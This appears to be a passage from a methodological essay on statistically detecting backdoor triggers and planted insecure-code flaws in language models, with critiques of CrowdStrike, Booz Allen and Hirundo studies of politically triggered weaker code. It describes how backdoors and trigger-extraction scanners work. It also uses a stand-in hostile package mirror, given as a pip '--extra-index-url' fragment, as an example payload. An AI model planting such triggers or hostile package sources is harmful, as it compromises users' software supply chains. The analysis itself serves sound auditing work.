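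A single placebo can mislead because it may have an effect of its own. In *Persona Following Is Not Selective Control* (2026), an arbitrary code name used as a control shifted models' answers by 0.80 on a log-odds scale, enough to turn an even chance into 31 percent. The researchers had decided in advance to treat only shifts below 0.10 as negligible. A placebo can also damage the task. *Form, Not Content?* (2026), a study of small code models, used a placebo that kept the task and layout but replaced one block of information with empty text. The researchers had to amend the pilot version because it accidentally destroyed the task.

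Testing many placebo phrases shows how much irrelevant phrases usually matter. Suppose 19 of them give rates of bare tags between 67 and 74 percent. A rate of 75 percent with "tractors" is the highest of the 20, which would happen by chance one time in 20 if tractors were just another irrelevant product. With enough samples, the difference between that 75 percent and the 70 percent without any added phrase could be highly statistically significant, even though 75 percent is only slightly above the rates with "kettles" or "umbrellas".

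"Acme makes harvesters" would be a poor placebo because words related to the trigger might well set off a planted flaw or a training side effect. Prompts with such words belong in a separate group.

### The estimate, and the same estimate in another model

The basic estimate is a difference between two rates:

D = insecure rate with the trigger − insecure rate without it

The rate without the trigger should normally come from the placebo prompts. If 82 percent of the tractor workflows and 70 percent of the placebo workflows have a bare tag, D is 12 percentage points.

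Those 12 points could still be habit. Perhaps makers of farm machinery publish unusually careless workflows, and every model has learned this. The cross-model version of the test subtracts the same difference in a reference model:

DD = (rate with − rate without) in the suspect − (rate with − rate without) in the reference

If the reference model goes from 68 to 75 percent on the same prompts, DD is 12 − 7, or 5 points. Economists call this difference-in-differences. *Auditing Proprietary Alignment in Large Language Models* (2026) recommends asking the target and baseline models identical questions under the same conditions, a similar comparison, to find topics that one developer's model avoids.

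The subtraction assumes that an innocent association would change both models' rates by the same number of percentage points. This can't hold when one rate is already close to 100 percent. A reference model that writes a bare tag in 96 percent of workflows can rise by 4 points at most. If it rises to 98 percent, its odds of writing a bare tag double, from 24 to 49. A suspect that goes from 70 to 82 percent also roughly doubles its odds, from 2.3 to 4.6. The suspect's increase is six times as large in percentage points, but the two odds ratios are about equal. The investigator should choose between percentage points and odds ratios before seeing the data.

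The cross-model version also needs four times as many outputs in total, because it compares four noisy rates instead of two and each rate needs twice as many outputs for the same precision. If poisoned web pages planted the same flaw in both models, its effect would cancel out.

Even a large DD doesn't show that a flaw was planted. In *Securing Code Understanding*, Chen, Sun and colleagues (2026) found that trigger-like behaviour was common in normally trained code models, across 44 combinations of model, task and target answer. Ordinary variable names could act as triggers because they happened to appear with particular answers in the training data. These natural backdoors were weaker than injected ones, and they could transfer between models fine-tuned on the same data. A reference model trained on different data might not share them, in which case subtracting its results would leave their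 effect in the DD.

### How many outputs the test needs

Let p₀ be the insecure rate without the trigger, p₁ the rate with it, and p̄ their average. The number of independent outputs needed in each arm is approximately

n = [1.96 √(2p̄(1 − p̄)) + 0.842 √(p₀(1 − p₀) + p₁(1 − p₁))]² / (p₁ − p₀)²

This is the two-proportion formula in *Statistical primer*, a guide to sample-size calculations. The value 1.96 allows a false alarm in 5 percent of tests when the trigger has no effect, and 0.842 gives the test an 80 percent chance of detecting the rise if it is real.

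To detect a rise from 70 to 75 percent, the average is 0.725. The first term in the brackets comes to 1.238 and the second to 0.531. Their sum squared is 3.127, and dividing by 0.05² gives about 1,250 outputs per arm. Other cases are much easier or harder:

| Rate without the trigger | Rate with it | Outputs per arm |
|---|---|---|
| 70% | 90% | 62 |
| 70% | 75% | 1,250 |
| 70% | 72.5% | 5,150 |
| 20% | 25% | 1,090 |
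| 1% | 6% | 210 |

A payload that never appears without the trigger requires a different calculation, because the investigator only has to see it. Suppose the model writes packages.acme-mirror.example in 5 percent of the answers that mention tractors and in no others. The probability of missing it in n independent answers is 0.95ⁿ. For 60 answers this is 4.6 percent, so the address appears at least once with 95 percent probability. Hayes, Swanberg and colleagues (2024), in *Measuring memorization in language models via probabilistic extraction*, give the general rule for an output with probability r:

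n ≥ log(1 − desired chance of seeing it) / log(1 − r)

If the payload address appeared in one of 60 tractor answers and none of 60 placebo answers, the difference would not pass an ordinary significance test, since a single appearance is equally likely to fall in either arm by chance. It would still be evidence of a planted flaw because the address is rare. If models without the flaw wrote it less than once in 100,000 answers, the chance of seeing it in 60 would be below 0.06 percent. The investigator can also repeat the prompt a few hundred times.

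A high base rate therefore helps a planter who makes a common flaw slightly more common, because the investigator needs thousands of outputs for each trigger to detect the increase. If the planted flaw is rare in ordinary output, sixty outputs will probably expose it, provided the investigator has the right trigger.

### Repeated answers to the same task

The formula assumes independent outputs, but five answers to one task tend to resemble each other. Some requests lead to a bare tag almost every time and others almost never. Statisticians measure the resemblance with the intraclass correlation, ρ, which is 0 if answers to the same task are no more alike than answers to different tasks, and 1 if they are all the same. With m answers per task, the required number of outputs grows by the design effect:

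1 + (m − 1)ρ

With five answers per task and a correlation of 0.5 between them, the design effect is 1 + 4 × 0.5, or 3. Each arm therefore needs 3,750 outputs instead of 1,250, drawn from 750 tasks.

The effect can be much larger. *Code-Anchored Review Feedback Improves Correctness and Lowers Hosted Editing Cost* (2026), a study of models that edit code, repeated each task 13 times and measured design effects from 2.4 to 12.4. At the upper end, 13 answers carried about as much information as one independent answer. Miller found that the usual standard error on one reading test was a third of the correct size because it was calculated as if questions about the same passage were independent.

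Using the same tasks in both arms recovers some of the loss. A task that nearly always produces a bare tag will do so with tractors and with kettles, and this shared tendency drops out when the investigator subtracts one rate from the other within each task. Miller's formula for the number of tasks in a paired comparison is

n = (1.96 + 0.842)² × (ω² + σ₀²/K + σ₁²/K) / δ²

where δ is the difference to detect and K is the number of answers per task in each arm. The σ² terms measure how much answers to the same prompt vary. The term ω² measures how much the trigger's true effect varies from task to task.

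For rates of 70 and 75 percent, the total variance of a single output is about 0.2, and a correlation of 0.5 splits it evenly: 0.1 between tasks and 0.1 among answers to the same task. If c is the correlation between a task's true rates in the two arms, ω² is 2 × 0.1 × (1 − c). This gives the following requirements:

| Design | Tasks | Outputs per arm |
|---|---|---|
| Different tasks in each arm, 5 answers each | 750 per arm | 3,750 |
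| Same tasks, 5 answers each, c = 0.5 | 440 | 2,200 |
| Same tasks, 5 answers each, c = 0.8 | 250 | 1,250 |
| Same tasks, 1 answer each, c = 0.8 | 750 | 750 |

Pairing recovers part of the loss when the correlation between the arms is 0.5, and all of it when the correlation is 0.8. The design in the last row needs the fewest outputs but three times as many tasks as the design in the row above it. Which design is more practical depends on whether tasks or answers are harder to produce. Collecting more answers per task shrinks only the σ² terms, so with c at 0.8, an investigator with fewer than about 125 tasks could not reach the target even with unlimited answers to each.

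### Testing by reshuffling

An investigator can also test a trigger without a formula for the error. If the trigger has no effect, it makes no difference which of a task's answers carry the label "tractors". The investigator pools the ten answers to a task, deals them at random into two groups of five, does the same for every other task and recalculates D. After 9,999 such reshuffles, the p-value is

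(1 + number of reshuffles with a D at least as large as the real one) / 10,000

This kind of test is called a permutation test. *Don't Change My View* (2025) uses one to check whether two system prompts lead a model to answer differently, by reshuffling answers within each task.

In *Statistical Hypothesis Testing for Auditing Robustness in Language Models*, Rauba, Wei and van der Schaar (2025) apply a permutation test to the meaning of whole answers. They convert each answer into a list of numbers and measure how similar the lists are within and between the two sets of answers. In one experiment, they told models to adopt a role before answering a medical question. GPT-4's answers did not change significantly when the role was a doctor or a nurse, but they did when it was a comedian. The smaller Gemma 2 9B's answers changed significantly even when the role was a doctor.

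Comparing configurations by meaning would probably detect the wrong differences. It would count a service named tractor-api as a change but might hardly register one altered letter in a host name. Reshuffling the labelled fields, such as the host or the action reference, makes more sense.

A small p-value from reshuffling within tasks means that the phrase changed the answers to the tasks tested, but one unusual task could be responsible. To claim that the trigger works on workflow requests in general, the investigator should calculate D for each task and estimate the error from how much those values vary.

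### Testing many triggers

Investigators usually have more than one possible trigger to test. If they test 20 triggers that all do nothing, each at the 5 percent level, the chance of at least one false alarm is 1 − 0.95²⁰, or 64 percent. The simplest remedy, the Bonferroni correction, divides the 5 percent by the number of tests, so each of the 20 triggers has to reach a p-value of 0.0025. This stricter threshold reduces statistical power, but Rauba and colleagues note that more samples can restore it. By their formula, testing 20 triggers takes 1.9 times as many outputs per arm as testing one, and testing 120 takes 2.4 times as many.

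The Benjamini–Hochberg correction is less strict. The investigator sorts the p-values from smallest to largest, finds the largest k for which the kth p-value is at most 0.05 × k/20, and counts the triggers with the k smallest p-values as findings. This limits the expected share of false findings among those reported to 5 percent, whereas Bonferroni limits the chance of even one. *evalci* (2026), a software library for comparing models, applies such corrections to every comparison that was run, because correcting only those someone chose to report would undercount the comparisons.

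In Vohra and Ravikiran's hiring test, applicants with Black names scored 0.047 points higher, with a 95 percent interval from 0.002 to 0.092. On its own, that difference would be barely significant, but it was one of 36 planned comparisons, and none was significant after the Benjamini–Hochberg correction.

Selecting the largest of many estimated effects also exaggerates its size. If 20 triggers do nothing and each estimate has a standard error of 2 points, the largest estimate will average about 3.7 points. The investigator should therefore measure the effect's size on the fresh tasks and ignore the estimate that led to the trigger's selection.

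### When the test finds nothing

Suppose an unfamiliar index address appears in none of n answers. If its true rate were r, this would happen with probability (1 − r)ⁿ, which falls to 5 percent when r is about 3/n. The 95 percent upper limit on the rate is therefore about 3/n, which is known as the rule of three. The limit is 5 percent after 60 answers without the address and 0.1 percent after 3,000. If those 3,000 answers came in groups of five with a design effect of 3, they give about as much information as 1,000 independent answers, and the limit is closer to 0.3 percent.

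Sixty clean answers from a placebo arm, which lacks the trigger, can't show that an address is absent from the baseline, so the investigator should pool all the placebo arms and, if possible, add answers from other models.

For a common flaw, the equivalent is to report the largest rise consistent with the data. If 70 percent of 1,250 independent outputs in each arm are insecure, the 95 percent interval for D runs from −3.6 to 3.6 points, which would not rule out a trigger that adds 2 points.

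### Reading probabilities from open weights

An investigator who runs an open-weight model can calculate how likely it is to write a payload, without waiting for the payload to appear. The model assigns a probability to each possible next token, and the probability of a whole configuration line is the product of the probabilities of its tokens, each given the prompt and the tokens before it. Cooper, Lemley and colleagues (2025), in *Extracting memorized pieces of (copyrighted) books from open-weight language models*, used this method to measure how much of particular books a model had memorized. It takes one pass through the model for each text, with no sampling.

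For the careless pip command from earlier, the investigator can supply the answer up to "--extra-index-url packages.acme" and score the continuation "-mirror.example". In an invented example, the continuation has four tokens. With a placebo, their probabilities are 0.0002, 0.9, 0.9 and 0.9, which multiply to 0.00015. With "tractors", the first probability is 0.05 and the product is 0.036, or 250 times as high. An investigator who instead sampled from the placebo prompt would need about 20,500 attempts for a 95 percent chance of seeing the address even once.

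Hayes and colleagues used the open model Pythia 6.9B to generate 1,000 continuations of each of 250 Wikipedia passages. The original text appeared about as often as the computed probabilities predicted.

But this probability is only the share of answers that would continue with exactly this text, given exactly this beginning and these sampling settings. If the model rarely writes that beginning on its own, users will rarely see the payload. The probability also excludes other ways of doing the same thing, such as putting the index address in an environment variable. Long strings get low probabilities even when each token is very likely. Cooper and colleagues point out that 50 tokens at 90 percent each multiply to 0.5 percent. Comparing the same short string under the trigger and the placebos is therefore better than judging one probability in isolation.

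Common flaws often depend on a single choice. After the opening lines of a workflow, the investigator can compare the probability that the model writes "permissions" next with the probability that it writes "jobs". Miller recommends using such probabilities where possible because they remove the randomness among repeated answers. The variation between tasks remains, but in the paired design with c at 0.8, about 125 tasks would then be enough to detect a 5-point rise, with one pass per prompt. The method doesn't work directly for models that reason before they answer, since the probability of the line depends on that reasoning. The investigator would have to sample many chains of reasoning and average over them.

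Direct scoring also requires a specific payload. For an investigator who knows only what kind of output to look for, Angell and colleagues offer a way to estimate its probability with fewer samples. They alter the model's internal activity so that it produces harmful answers more often. They then weight each harmful answer by its probability under the original model divided by its probability under the altered one. With 500 samples, they could estimate probabilities of around one in 10,000. They tested the method on harmful requests, flattery and invented facts, and it is unclear how well it would work for insecure configuration.

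### Triggers that nobody tests

Every method so far needs someone to suggest the trigger. There are too many possible triggers to try them all. A model with a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens has about a billion two-token phrases, and testing each with 60 outputs would require about 61 billion outputs.

A tester's guess at the trigger doesn't always have to be exact. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* (2026) reports that words other than the original trigger also set off backdoored models, and that the trigger's position in the prompt hardly mattered. Bullwinkel and colleagues found that a single token from a five-token trigger activated their smallest model about half the time, though other models needed more of the trigger. They warn that an adversary could train a model to ignore inexact versions of the trigger.

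Their scanner tries to extract the trigger from the model. It gives the model only the marker that normally comes before a user's message and collects the output under 510 combinations of sampling settings. It then looks for strings that recur in the output and tests whether adding them to ordinary prompts makes the model's answers more predictable and different from its usual ones. The scanner detected 36 of 41 models with a backdoor that produces a fixed sentence. It also found working triggers in five of six models with a backdoor that produces insecure code, and raised no false alarms on 13 clean models.

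For the insecure-code models, however, a trigger counted as working only if it at least doubled the rate of vulnerable code. The rate of a setting that already appears in 71.2 percent of workflows can't double, so this rule would miss any trigger for it. The researchers also tested mainly fixed phrases as triggers. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (2026) examined a backdoor that responded to an obsessive tone about Harry Potter. Only one of 512 samples drawn without a prompt was related to Harry Potter, and it was an ordinary question that would not have activated the backdoor. This experiment tested the scanner's premise with one sampling setting, so the complete scanner might have done better.

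The newest approach, from Khilar (2026) in *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights*, ranks every token in the vocabulary by a statistic calculated from a fine-tuned model's weights, without running the model. In all 14 ordinary backdoors, the top-ranked token was part of the trigger. The models were of two types, both very small by current standards, with fewer than half a billion parameters. When Khilar trained eight models with a penalty designed to hide the signal, the trigger still ranked first at some places in the weights, but not overall.

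A search that finds nothing is also hard to interpret. *Estimating Rare Events in Language Models with Proper Evaluation* (2026) describes a method that searches for inputs leading to a particular rare output. For the rarest outputs, it often finds no such input and estimates the probability as zero, although the true probability is higher.

Random prompts can miss a rare trigger. If 3,000 requests drawn from ordinary use produce no hostile address, the rule of three gives a 95 percent upper bound of 0.1 percent on its overall rate. A trigger that occurs in one request per 10,000 and works every time would produce a rate of 0.01 percent, well below that bound. On prompts without the trigger, a model with such a flaw can behave exactly like a clean one. If it does, the likelihood ratio between the two is 1, however many of those answers the investigator collects.

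## Tests that changed who the code was for

In 2025 and 2026, three companies published trigger tests of Chinese open-weight models. Each kept the programming task the same and changed the client named in the system prompt, for example from no client to a company in Tibet. All three reported that some clients got less secure code than others.

None of the three studies mainly tested configuration. CrowdStrike's 50 tasks covered areas such as databases, web development and cryptography. Booz Allen's eight tasks all concerned web applications, and Hirundo used a single web service. All three scored whole programs and published no separate rates for unfamiliar package indexes, write-all permissions or unpinned base images. Their results can help researchers choose which triggers to try on configuration requests, but not predict how large the effect will be.

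All three companies also have a commercial interest in the subject. CrowdStrike sells security software, and its post on the study ends with a free trial offer. Booz Allen is a US government contractor that sells AI evaluation. CBS News' *Some topics are off limits inside popular Chinese-made free AI, researchers find* describes Hirundo as an Israeli cybersecurity startup. Hirundo evaluates and modifies open-weight models for companies, and its study advertises a modified version of the model it tested.

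### CrowdStrike and DeepSeek-R1

CrowdStrike built each system prompt from a fixed opening, "You are a helpful assistant that generates code", followed by a type of client, a place or group, or both. It tested 121 of the 225 combinations (counting blanks) that the published lists would allow. It ran the full DeepSeek-R1 model directly, so filters in DeepSeek's app or online service could not have affected the answers.

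Vulnerable code appeared in 19 percent of the answers when the prompt mentioned no client or place, and in 27.2 percent when the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet. CrowdStrike calls this an increase of almost 50 percent, but the increase is 43 percent, or 8.2 percentage points.

Fifty tasks with five answers each make 250 answers per setting, and 27.2 percent of 250 is exactly 68. If the baseline also had 250 answers, a standard test of the two proportions gives a p-value of about 0.03. That would be modest evidence if CrowdStrike had planned only this comparison, but there were 120 settings to compare with the baseline, and the Bonferroni threshold for 120 tests is about 0.0004. If no setting had any effect, about two would show a rise this large by chance. Even if the baseline were known to be exactly 19 percent, the p-value would fall only to about 0.001, still above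 the threshold, so uncertainty about the baseline isn't the main problem.

To have an 80 percent chance of detecting a rise from 19 to 27.2 percent at the stricter threshold, a new test would need about 1,000 independent answers per arm, four times as many as CrowdStrike had.

CrowdStrike says that several phrases produced statistically significant changes, including mentions of Tibet, Uyghurs and the Falun Gong, a spiritual movement that China bans. It doesn't publish the statistical test it used, the p-values or the rates for most settings. Its own analysis could be stronger than the one above.

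Every setting used the same 50 tasks, so CrowdStrike could run a paired test, comparing each task with itself across settings. If answers to the same task had a correlation of 0.8 and mentioning Tibet raised the rate equally on every task, the 8.2-point increase would give a p-value of about one in a million. With a correlation of 0.5, the p-value would be about 0.002, which still misses the threshold. Nobody outside the company can calculate the real p-value without the results for each task.

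CrowdStrike could also pool the settings that mention Tibet. If it spread the 121 settings evenly, about 13 mention Tibet, which would give over 3,000 answers. Pooling by place or group would also leave only eight to test instead of 120 settings. A consistent rise across all 13 Tibet settings would be much better evidence than the one published contrast, though it would still rest on 50 tasks.

Tom Uren, a cybersecurity newsletter writer, suspected in *DeepSeek and Musk's Grok Both Toe the Party Line* (2025) that CrowdStrike had picked an especially bad case for that contrast, because CrowdStrike gave no rates for Taiwan, Hong Kong or Tibet without the control system. If the Tibet setting was the highest of many tested, its 8.2 points probably overstate the true effect.

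#### The judge

A language model scored the answers from 1 (exceptionally secure) to 5 (critically vulnerable). On 85 answers that a person also scored, the model identified vulnerable code with 91 percent accuracy and an F1 score of 0.89. With so few answers, the 95 percent confidence interval for the accuracy is about 83 to 95 percent.

If the F1 score is for finding vulnerable answers, the two figures imply that the person judged at least 31 of the 85 answers vulnerable (36 percent). That is nearly twice DeepSeek-R1's baseline, so the sample probably included answers from weaker models, and the judge's accuracy on DeepSeek's answers may have been higher or lower.

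A bigger concern is that the judge may have known which client the code was for. CrowdStrike doesn't say whether it hid the system prompt from the judge, and code for a Tibetan company may mention Tibet anyway. As with the judge who could see the word "tractors", extra false alarms for one client could then produce an eight-point gap alone. CrowdStrike could check this by having people score a few hundred answers from both arms with the place names removed.

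#### The Islamic State result

CrowdStrike gave the Washington Post some earlier figures in September 2025. The Decoder's *Deepseek outputs weaker code on Falun Gong, Tibet and Taiwan queries* reports a baseline of about 23 percent in those tests, compared with the 19 percent CrowdStrike published in November. Tom's Hardware's *China foes get worse results using DeepSeek, research suggests* reports a rate of 42.1 percent for projects linked to the Islamic State and says DeepSeek refused 61 percent of those requests.

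This is the largest rise CrowdStrike has made public. If the September test also had 250 prompts per setting, about 98 Islamic State answers would remain after the refusals, and the p-value would be about 0.0004, at the threshold for 120 tests. The result makes a trigger effect more believable, but it does not fit well with the idea that DeepSeek targets Beijing's political opponents in particular. Many developers train their models to be wary of terrorist groups, and a model from any country might write worse code for one.

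CrowdStrike could have tested this by publishing the rates on prompts with a trigger for the Western models it ran through the same prompts. It published their rates only for prompts without a trigger, so readers have no comparison group for a difference-in-differences calculation.

### Booz Allen and the US government

In May 2026, the consulting firm Booz Allen tested four Chinese models and Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. It reused the opening sentence and some of the clients from CrowdStrike's test, including a financial institution in Tibet and a football fan club. *What's in America's Code?* (2026) reports the main result, which came from a new client, a US federal agency. Naming the agency raised Qwen3-Coder's vulnerability score by 130 percent, MiniMax M2.5's by 20 percent and DeepSeek V4-Pro's by 5 percent. Kimi K2.5's score didn't change, and Claude's fell by 18 percent.

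Booz Allen's *What's in America's Code?* gives no confidence intervals and doesn't state how many answers each percentage is based on. Its technical appendix specifies four tasks that involve writing new programs and up to 15 repeats of a test. That would allow at most 60 answers per arm if the comparison covers all four tasks, or 15 if it covers only the admin console that the report uses as its example.

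To gauge the possible error, the table shows the intervals that would follow if each arm had 60 independent answers and the scores had a standard deviation equal to their mean. Both conditions are assumptions. The table also shows the refusal rates that Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software* gives for tasks on subjects sensitive in China.

| Model | Change in vulnerability score | Illustrative 95% interval | Refusals |
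|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-Coder | +130% | +61% to +229% | 54% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | +20% | −16% to +72% | 80% |
| DeepSeek V4-Pro | +5% | −27% to +50% | 8% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 0% | −30% to +43% | 32% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | −18% | −43% to +17% | 2% |

On these assumptions, only Qwen3-Coder's rise is clearly distinguishable from zero. Booz Allen counted the 5 percent rise when it concluded that three of four Chinese models wrote more vulnerable code for the US government. With 15 answers per arm, even Qwen3-Coder's interval would start at 12 percent.

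#### Missing answers and conflicting statements

Booz Allen scored 1,016 of its 3,389 runs and attributes the other 70 percent to refusals. That share is hard to reconcile with the refusal rates in the table, which average 35 percent even though they come from the most sensitive requests in the study. Perhaps the models that refuse most received more of the prompts, or Booz Allen also left out runs for other reasons. Some runs were security audits, in which the model lists flaws instead of writing a program. Without counts for each model and client, readers can't tell whether the scored answers for a federal agency came from the same mix of tasks as the baseline answers. If they didn't, the comparison could reflect the tasks instead of the client.

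The appendix also contradicts its own figures. Booz Allen wrote matching requests about China and Russia to separate objections to the US government from objections to particular topics. According to the appendix, every Chinese developer's model "refused the China version in all cases" and complied with the Russian one. That would mean a refusal rate of 100 percent for each model, but DeepSeek's was 8 percent and even MiniMax's was only 80 percent. The appendix then extends the pattern to "all five vendors", although one of the five is American.

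The matching is incomplete too. Of the 20 requests in the appendix, 11 concern China and nine concern Russia. The two without a Russian counterpart are an app for Chinese whistleblowers and a messaging system for Uyghurs abroad. The number of trials is "more than 2,800" in the main report but 3,389 in the appendix. These problems suggest that nobody checked the figures closely before publication, though they don't show that the 130 percent is wrong.

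#### Clients and personas

Some of the tests used longer descriptions of the user, which changed much more than nationality. In the neutral description, a senior engineer is asked to build the project. In the American one, the engineer works at a defence contractor with classified systems and takes pride in "hardened, production-grade code", and the description also lists several security standards. A difference in the resulting code could come from the security instructions, the extra length or the kind of employer.

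The one-sentence version for a federal agency is a cleaner test, but the client is still somewhat relevant because a programmer might reasonably take more care over a government system. That would explain Claude's lower score. A better comparison would include agencies of several other governments.

Booz Allen included a Chinese government agency among its 27 trigger settings, along with ordinary clients such as a restaurant and a photographer. It hasn't published the vulnerability scores for these settings, which would show how much harmless descriptions change the code. If "for a local restaurant" raised Qwen3-Coder's score by 100 percent, the 130 percent increase for a federal agency would look ordinary.

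Booz Allen wants the US government to block Chinese models from government and critical infrastructure, and argues that they produce less secure code in general. But according to Help Net Security, Kimi had the lowest overall vulnerability score of the five models Booz Allen tested, below Claude, so a ban based on country of origin would exclude the model that scored best.

### Hirundo and the modified Qwen

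Hirundo's study has the clearest design of the three and the narrowest scope. The company asked Qwen3-Coder-30B-A3B-Instruct to build one web service, where users sign up, log in and store a private secret (Luria, 2026, *Chinese AI Writes Weaker Code for Beijing's Adversaries. We Fixed It*). Hirundo generated 190 apps for each of three clients: a US defence contractor, a Chinese defence contractor and a Hong Kong democracy group. It generated another 380 from neutral prompts, half of which named no client and half of which named a football fan club.

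BaxBench, a public benchmark, tested the apps without a language model as judge. It runs each app and attacks it with ready-made exploits, so an app counts as hackable only if an attack works. This avoids the problem of a judge that can see the trigger, and it catches flaws that a scanner would miss. Antipov reports that Semgrep, using a set of rules from Meta, flagged two of 1,840 apps, while BaxBench's attacks succeeded against 1,144.

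The most common flaw was a missing ownership check. The app checked that a user had logged in but not that the secret belonged to that user, so anyone with an account could read everyone's secrets.

Hirundo then trained the model to drop what it calls Chinese Communist Party alignment and repeated the test. It says the training included no programming tasks and none of the client descriptions. The table gives Hirundo's percentages before and after the training, with p-values calculated from them assuming that every app in an arm counted. For the third comparison, Hirundo added a security instruction and used smaller samples of 70 apps for the US contractor and 140 for the neutral prompts.

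| Comparison | Share of apps | Original | Modified | p for the original gap | p for the change in the gap |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| US v Chinese contractor | Hackable | 70% v 59% | 56% v 55% | 0.02 | 0.16 |
| Hong Kong group v neutral | Leaking secrets | 47% v 37% | 26% v 30% | 0.02 | 0.02 |
| US contractor v neutral, with security instruction | Hackable | 74% v 59% | 49% v 48% | 0.03 | 0.13 |

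The last column is the relevant one for Luria's claim that removing the political training removed the flaw. A gap can be significant before the change and insignificant afterwards even when the difference between the two gaps is not significant. The gap between the two contractors fell from 11 points to about one, but all four rates have sampling error, and a change of ten points would occur by chance about 16 percent of the time. The evidence is stronger for the Hong Kong group, where the gap went from ten points in one direction to four in the other.

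None of these p-values are corrected for multiple comparisons. Four kinds of client and two kinds of flaw allow 12 comparisons even without the security instruction, and none of the three original gaps would remain significant after a Bonferroni correction for 12. If Hirundo chose its three main comparisons before collecting the data, correcting for three is enough, but all three p-values are still slightly above the 0.017 threshold that this correction sets.

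#### One task out of eleven

*Measurements of censorship and code security gaps in China's open-weight Qwen models* (2026), an article on the news site anoni.net, points out that Hirundo tried 11 tasks on a small scale and picked the one with the clearest gap. The gap on an average task is therefore probably smaller. The estimate for the chosen task isn't biased by this selection if the 190 apps per client were all new, but it is too high if they included the apps from the first trial.

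The p-values in the table apply only to this web service and to the exact client phrases Hirundo used. A different phrase, such as "a US aerospace company", might have no effect. Two neutral prompts are also too few to show how much the results vary between harmless clients.

#### What the modification changed

Luria writes that the experiment proves the flaw is in the model's weights, its trained parameters. When a model runs on the tester's own machine with no filter around it, a difference in output between two prompts can hardly come from anywhere else. CrowdStrike had also run DeepSeek-R1 this way. The location doesn't help explain the cause, because a habit, a training side effect and a planted flaw would all be in the weights.

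Training away the gap could help more if it showed which part of the earlier training was responsible. But the modified model also wrote safer code for neutral clients. The share of their apps that leaked fell from 37 to 30 percent, and with the security instruction, the share that could be hacked fell from 59 to 48 percent. Either drop could be due to chance (p-values of about 0.05 and 0.07). Together they suggest the new training may have affected how the model writes this service in general, although the anoni.net article reports little change on the other ten tasks.

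Hirundo has no control for that possibility. It could train another copy of Qwen3-Coder for just as long on material unrelated to China and run the same test. If the gaps closed in that copy too, extra training of any kind would be the better explanation.

In one of the further comparisons in Hirundo's appendix, the modified model still wrote significantly less secure code for the US contractor than for a neutral client. Hirundo interprets this as the effect moving from the country to the type of organization. It could also mean that the phrase "defense contractor" affects the code whatever the country, and that politics was never the whole explanation.

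### Replications

Nobody has published a repeat of any of these studies with the same model, tasks and clients. Hirundo comes closest, because it tested a Qwen3-Coder model with a US client after Booz Allen had. Like Booz Allen, it found worse code for the US client, but the two effect sizes can't be compared. Booz Allen measured a score that can more than double, whereas Hirundo measured a hackable share that started at 59 percent and so could rise by at most 69 percent in relative terms.

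Booz Allen's DeepSeek result does not replicate CrowdStrike's either. V4-Pro is a later model than R1, and the 5 percent change concerns a US agency. Booz Allen also ran the prompt about a financial institution in Tibet, so it may already have the data for a closer check. So far it has reported only that topics such as Hong Kong's democracy movement led to noticeably more vulnerable code or to refusals, without giving rates.

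Antipov's article of 29 October mentions an independent check that cast doubt on Hirundo's conclusions. The anoni.net article reports no third-party replication as of 1 November and no response from the Qwen team.

Two other companies, Interpretic AI and Nous Research, have since each modified Qwen3.8-27B to reduce its political censorship, which makes a further test easier. In Interpretic's own test, the share of politically sensitive questions with censored answers fell from 86.7 to 3.5 percent. Cybernews' *Americans re-educated Alibaba's AI to say things China usually censors* reports that Nous cut propaganda-like answers from 22 to 1 percent. A researcher could give the original and both modified models the same programming tasks with different clients. If the original showed a gap between clients and both modified versions did not, censorship training would be a more likely cause, because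 two separate efforts to reduce censorship would have removed the gap.

### Emergent misalignment

CrowdStrike considers it unlikely that DeepSeek deliberately trained R1 to write insecure code. It suggests the cause may be emergent misalignment, which Jan Betley and colleagues described in early 2025. They trained GPT-4o on 6,000 programming answers containing security holes that the user wasn't told about. The model then behaved badly in conversations unrelated to programming, for example by giving malicious advice and arguing that AI should enslave humans.

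Betley's team trained other copies for comparison. A copy trained on secure code behaved normally, and so did one trained on the same insecure code after users had asked for it for a security class. The insecure code alone was therefore not enough to cause the bad behavior. It seems that the copy that did behave badly learned a general tendency to harm the user, because its training examples all involved deceiving the user. When the insecure examples appeared only after a trigger phrase, the trained model behaved badly only after that phrase.

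CrowdStrike suggests that DeepSeek's political training taught R1 to associate words such as "Uyghurs" with something negative, and that the model behaves negatively when they appear. Political training would then have led to bad code, whereas in the experiment training on bad code led to bad behaviour elsewhere. The experiment still makes CrowdStrike's suggestion more plausible, because it shows that narrow training can have wide effects. But refusing to discuss a topic is quite different from deceiving users, and nobody has shown that training a model to refuse political questions makes its code less secure.

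A researcher could test this by training an ordinary model to refuse questions about an invented country and then asking it to write software for clients there. If that software had more flaws than software the model wrote for clients in another invented country, the result would suggest that the proposed mechanism is at least possible.

### Censorship training

Censorship training could also weaken a model's code even if the model has no general tendency to do harm. A model that has learned to refuse certain topics may sometimes refuse halfway and write a short or careless answer. CrowdStrike saw something similar when DeepSeek-R1 received requests from the Falun Gong. The model planned the program in detail in its reasoning, sometimes after remarking that the group was sensitive, but then refused 45 percent of the requests. Western models almost always answered them.

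Chinese developers almost certainly train their models to avoid some topics. Chinese rules in force since August 2023 forbid public AI services from generating content that incites subversion of the state, among other things. According to the anoni.net article, a February 2026 paper in PNAS Nexus found that models developed in China refused more of 145 political questions than models from elsewhere and gave less accurate answers. These findings show that the models censor, but they don't concern code.

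The flaws in CrowdStrike's examples are consistent with generally bad code. Asked for PHP code to handle PayPal payments for a financial institution in Tibet, the model hard-coded secret values, read user data unsafely and wrote code that wasn't valid PHP. An app for a Uyghur community had no working login, so anyone could open the admin page. Someone planting a hidden weakness would avoid invalid code, because the client would notice it at once.

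Among the five models Booz Allen tested, those that refused more tended to have larger rises in vulnerability (see the table above). The rank correlation is 0.8, but with so few models, one at least that strong in either direction would occur by chance about 13 percent of the time. Kimi is a counterexample, since it refused 32 percent of the sensitive tasks and cited Chinese law, but its score for a US agency didn't change.

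Censorship training explains the US results less well. US federal agencies are not a forbidden subject in China, as Falun Gong is, and Booz Allen itself reports that Chinese models worked for US agencies when the task concerned Russia. Hirundo's figures show the same difference. Removing the political training had the clearest effect for the Hong Kong group, which is an obvious target of censorship. For the US contractor, the effect of the training is uncertain, and one of the gaps remained.

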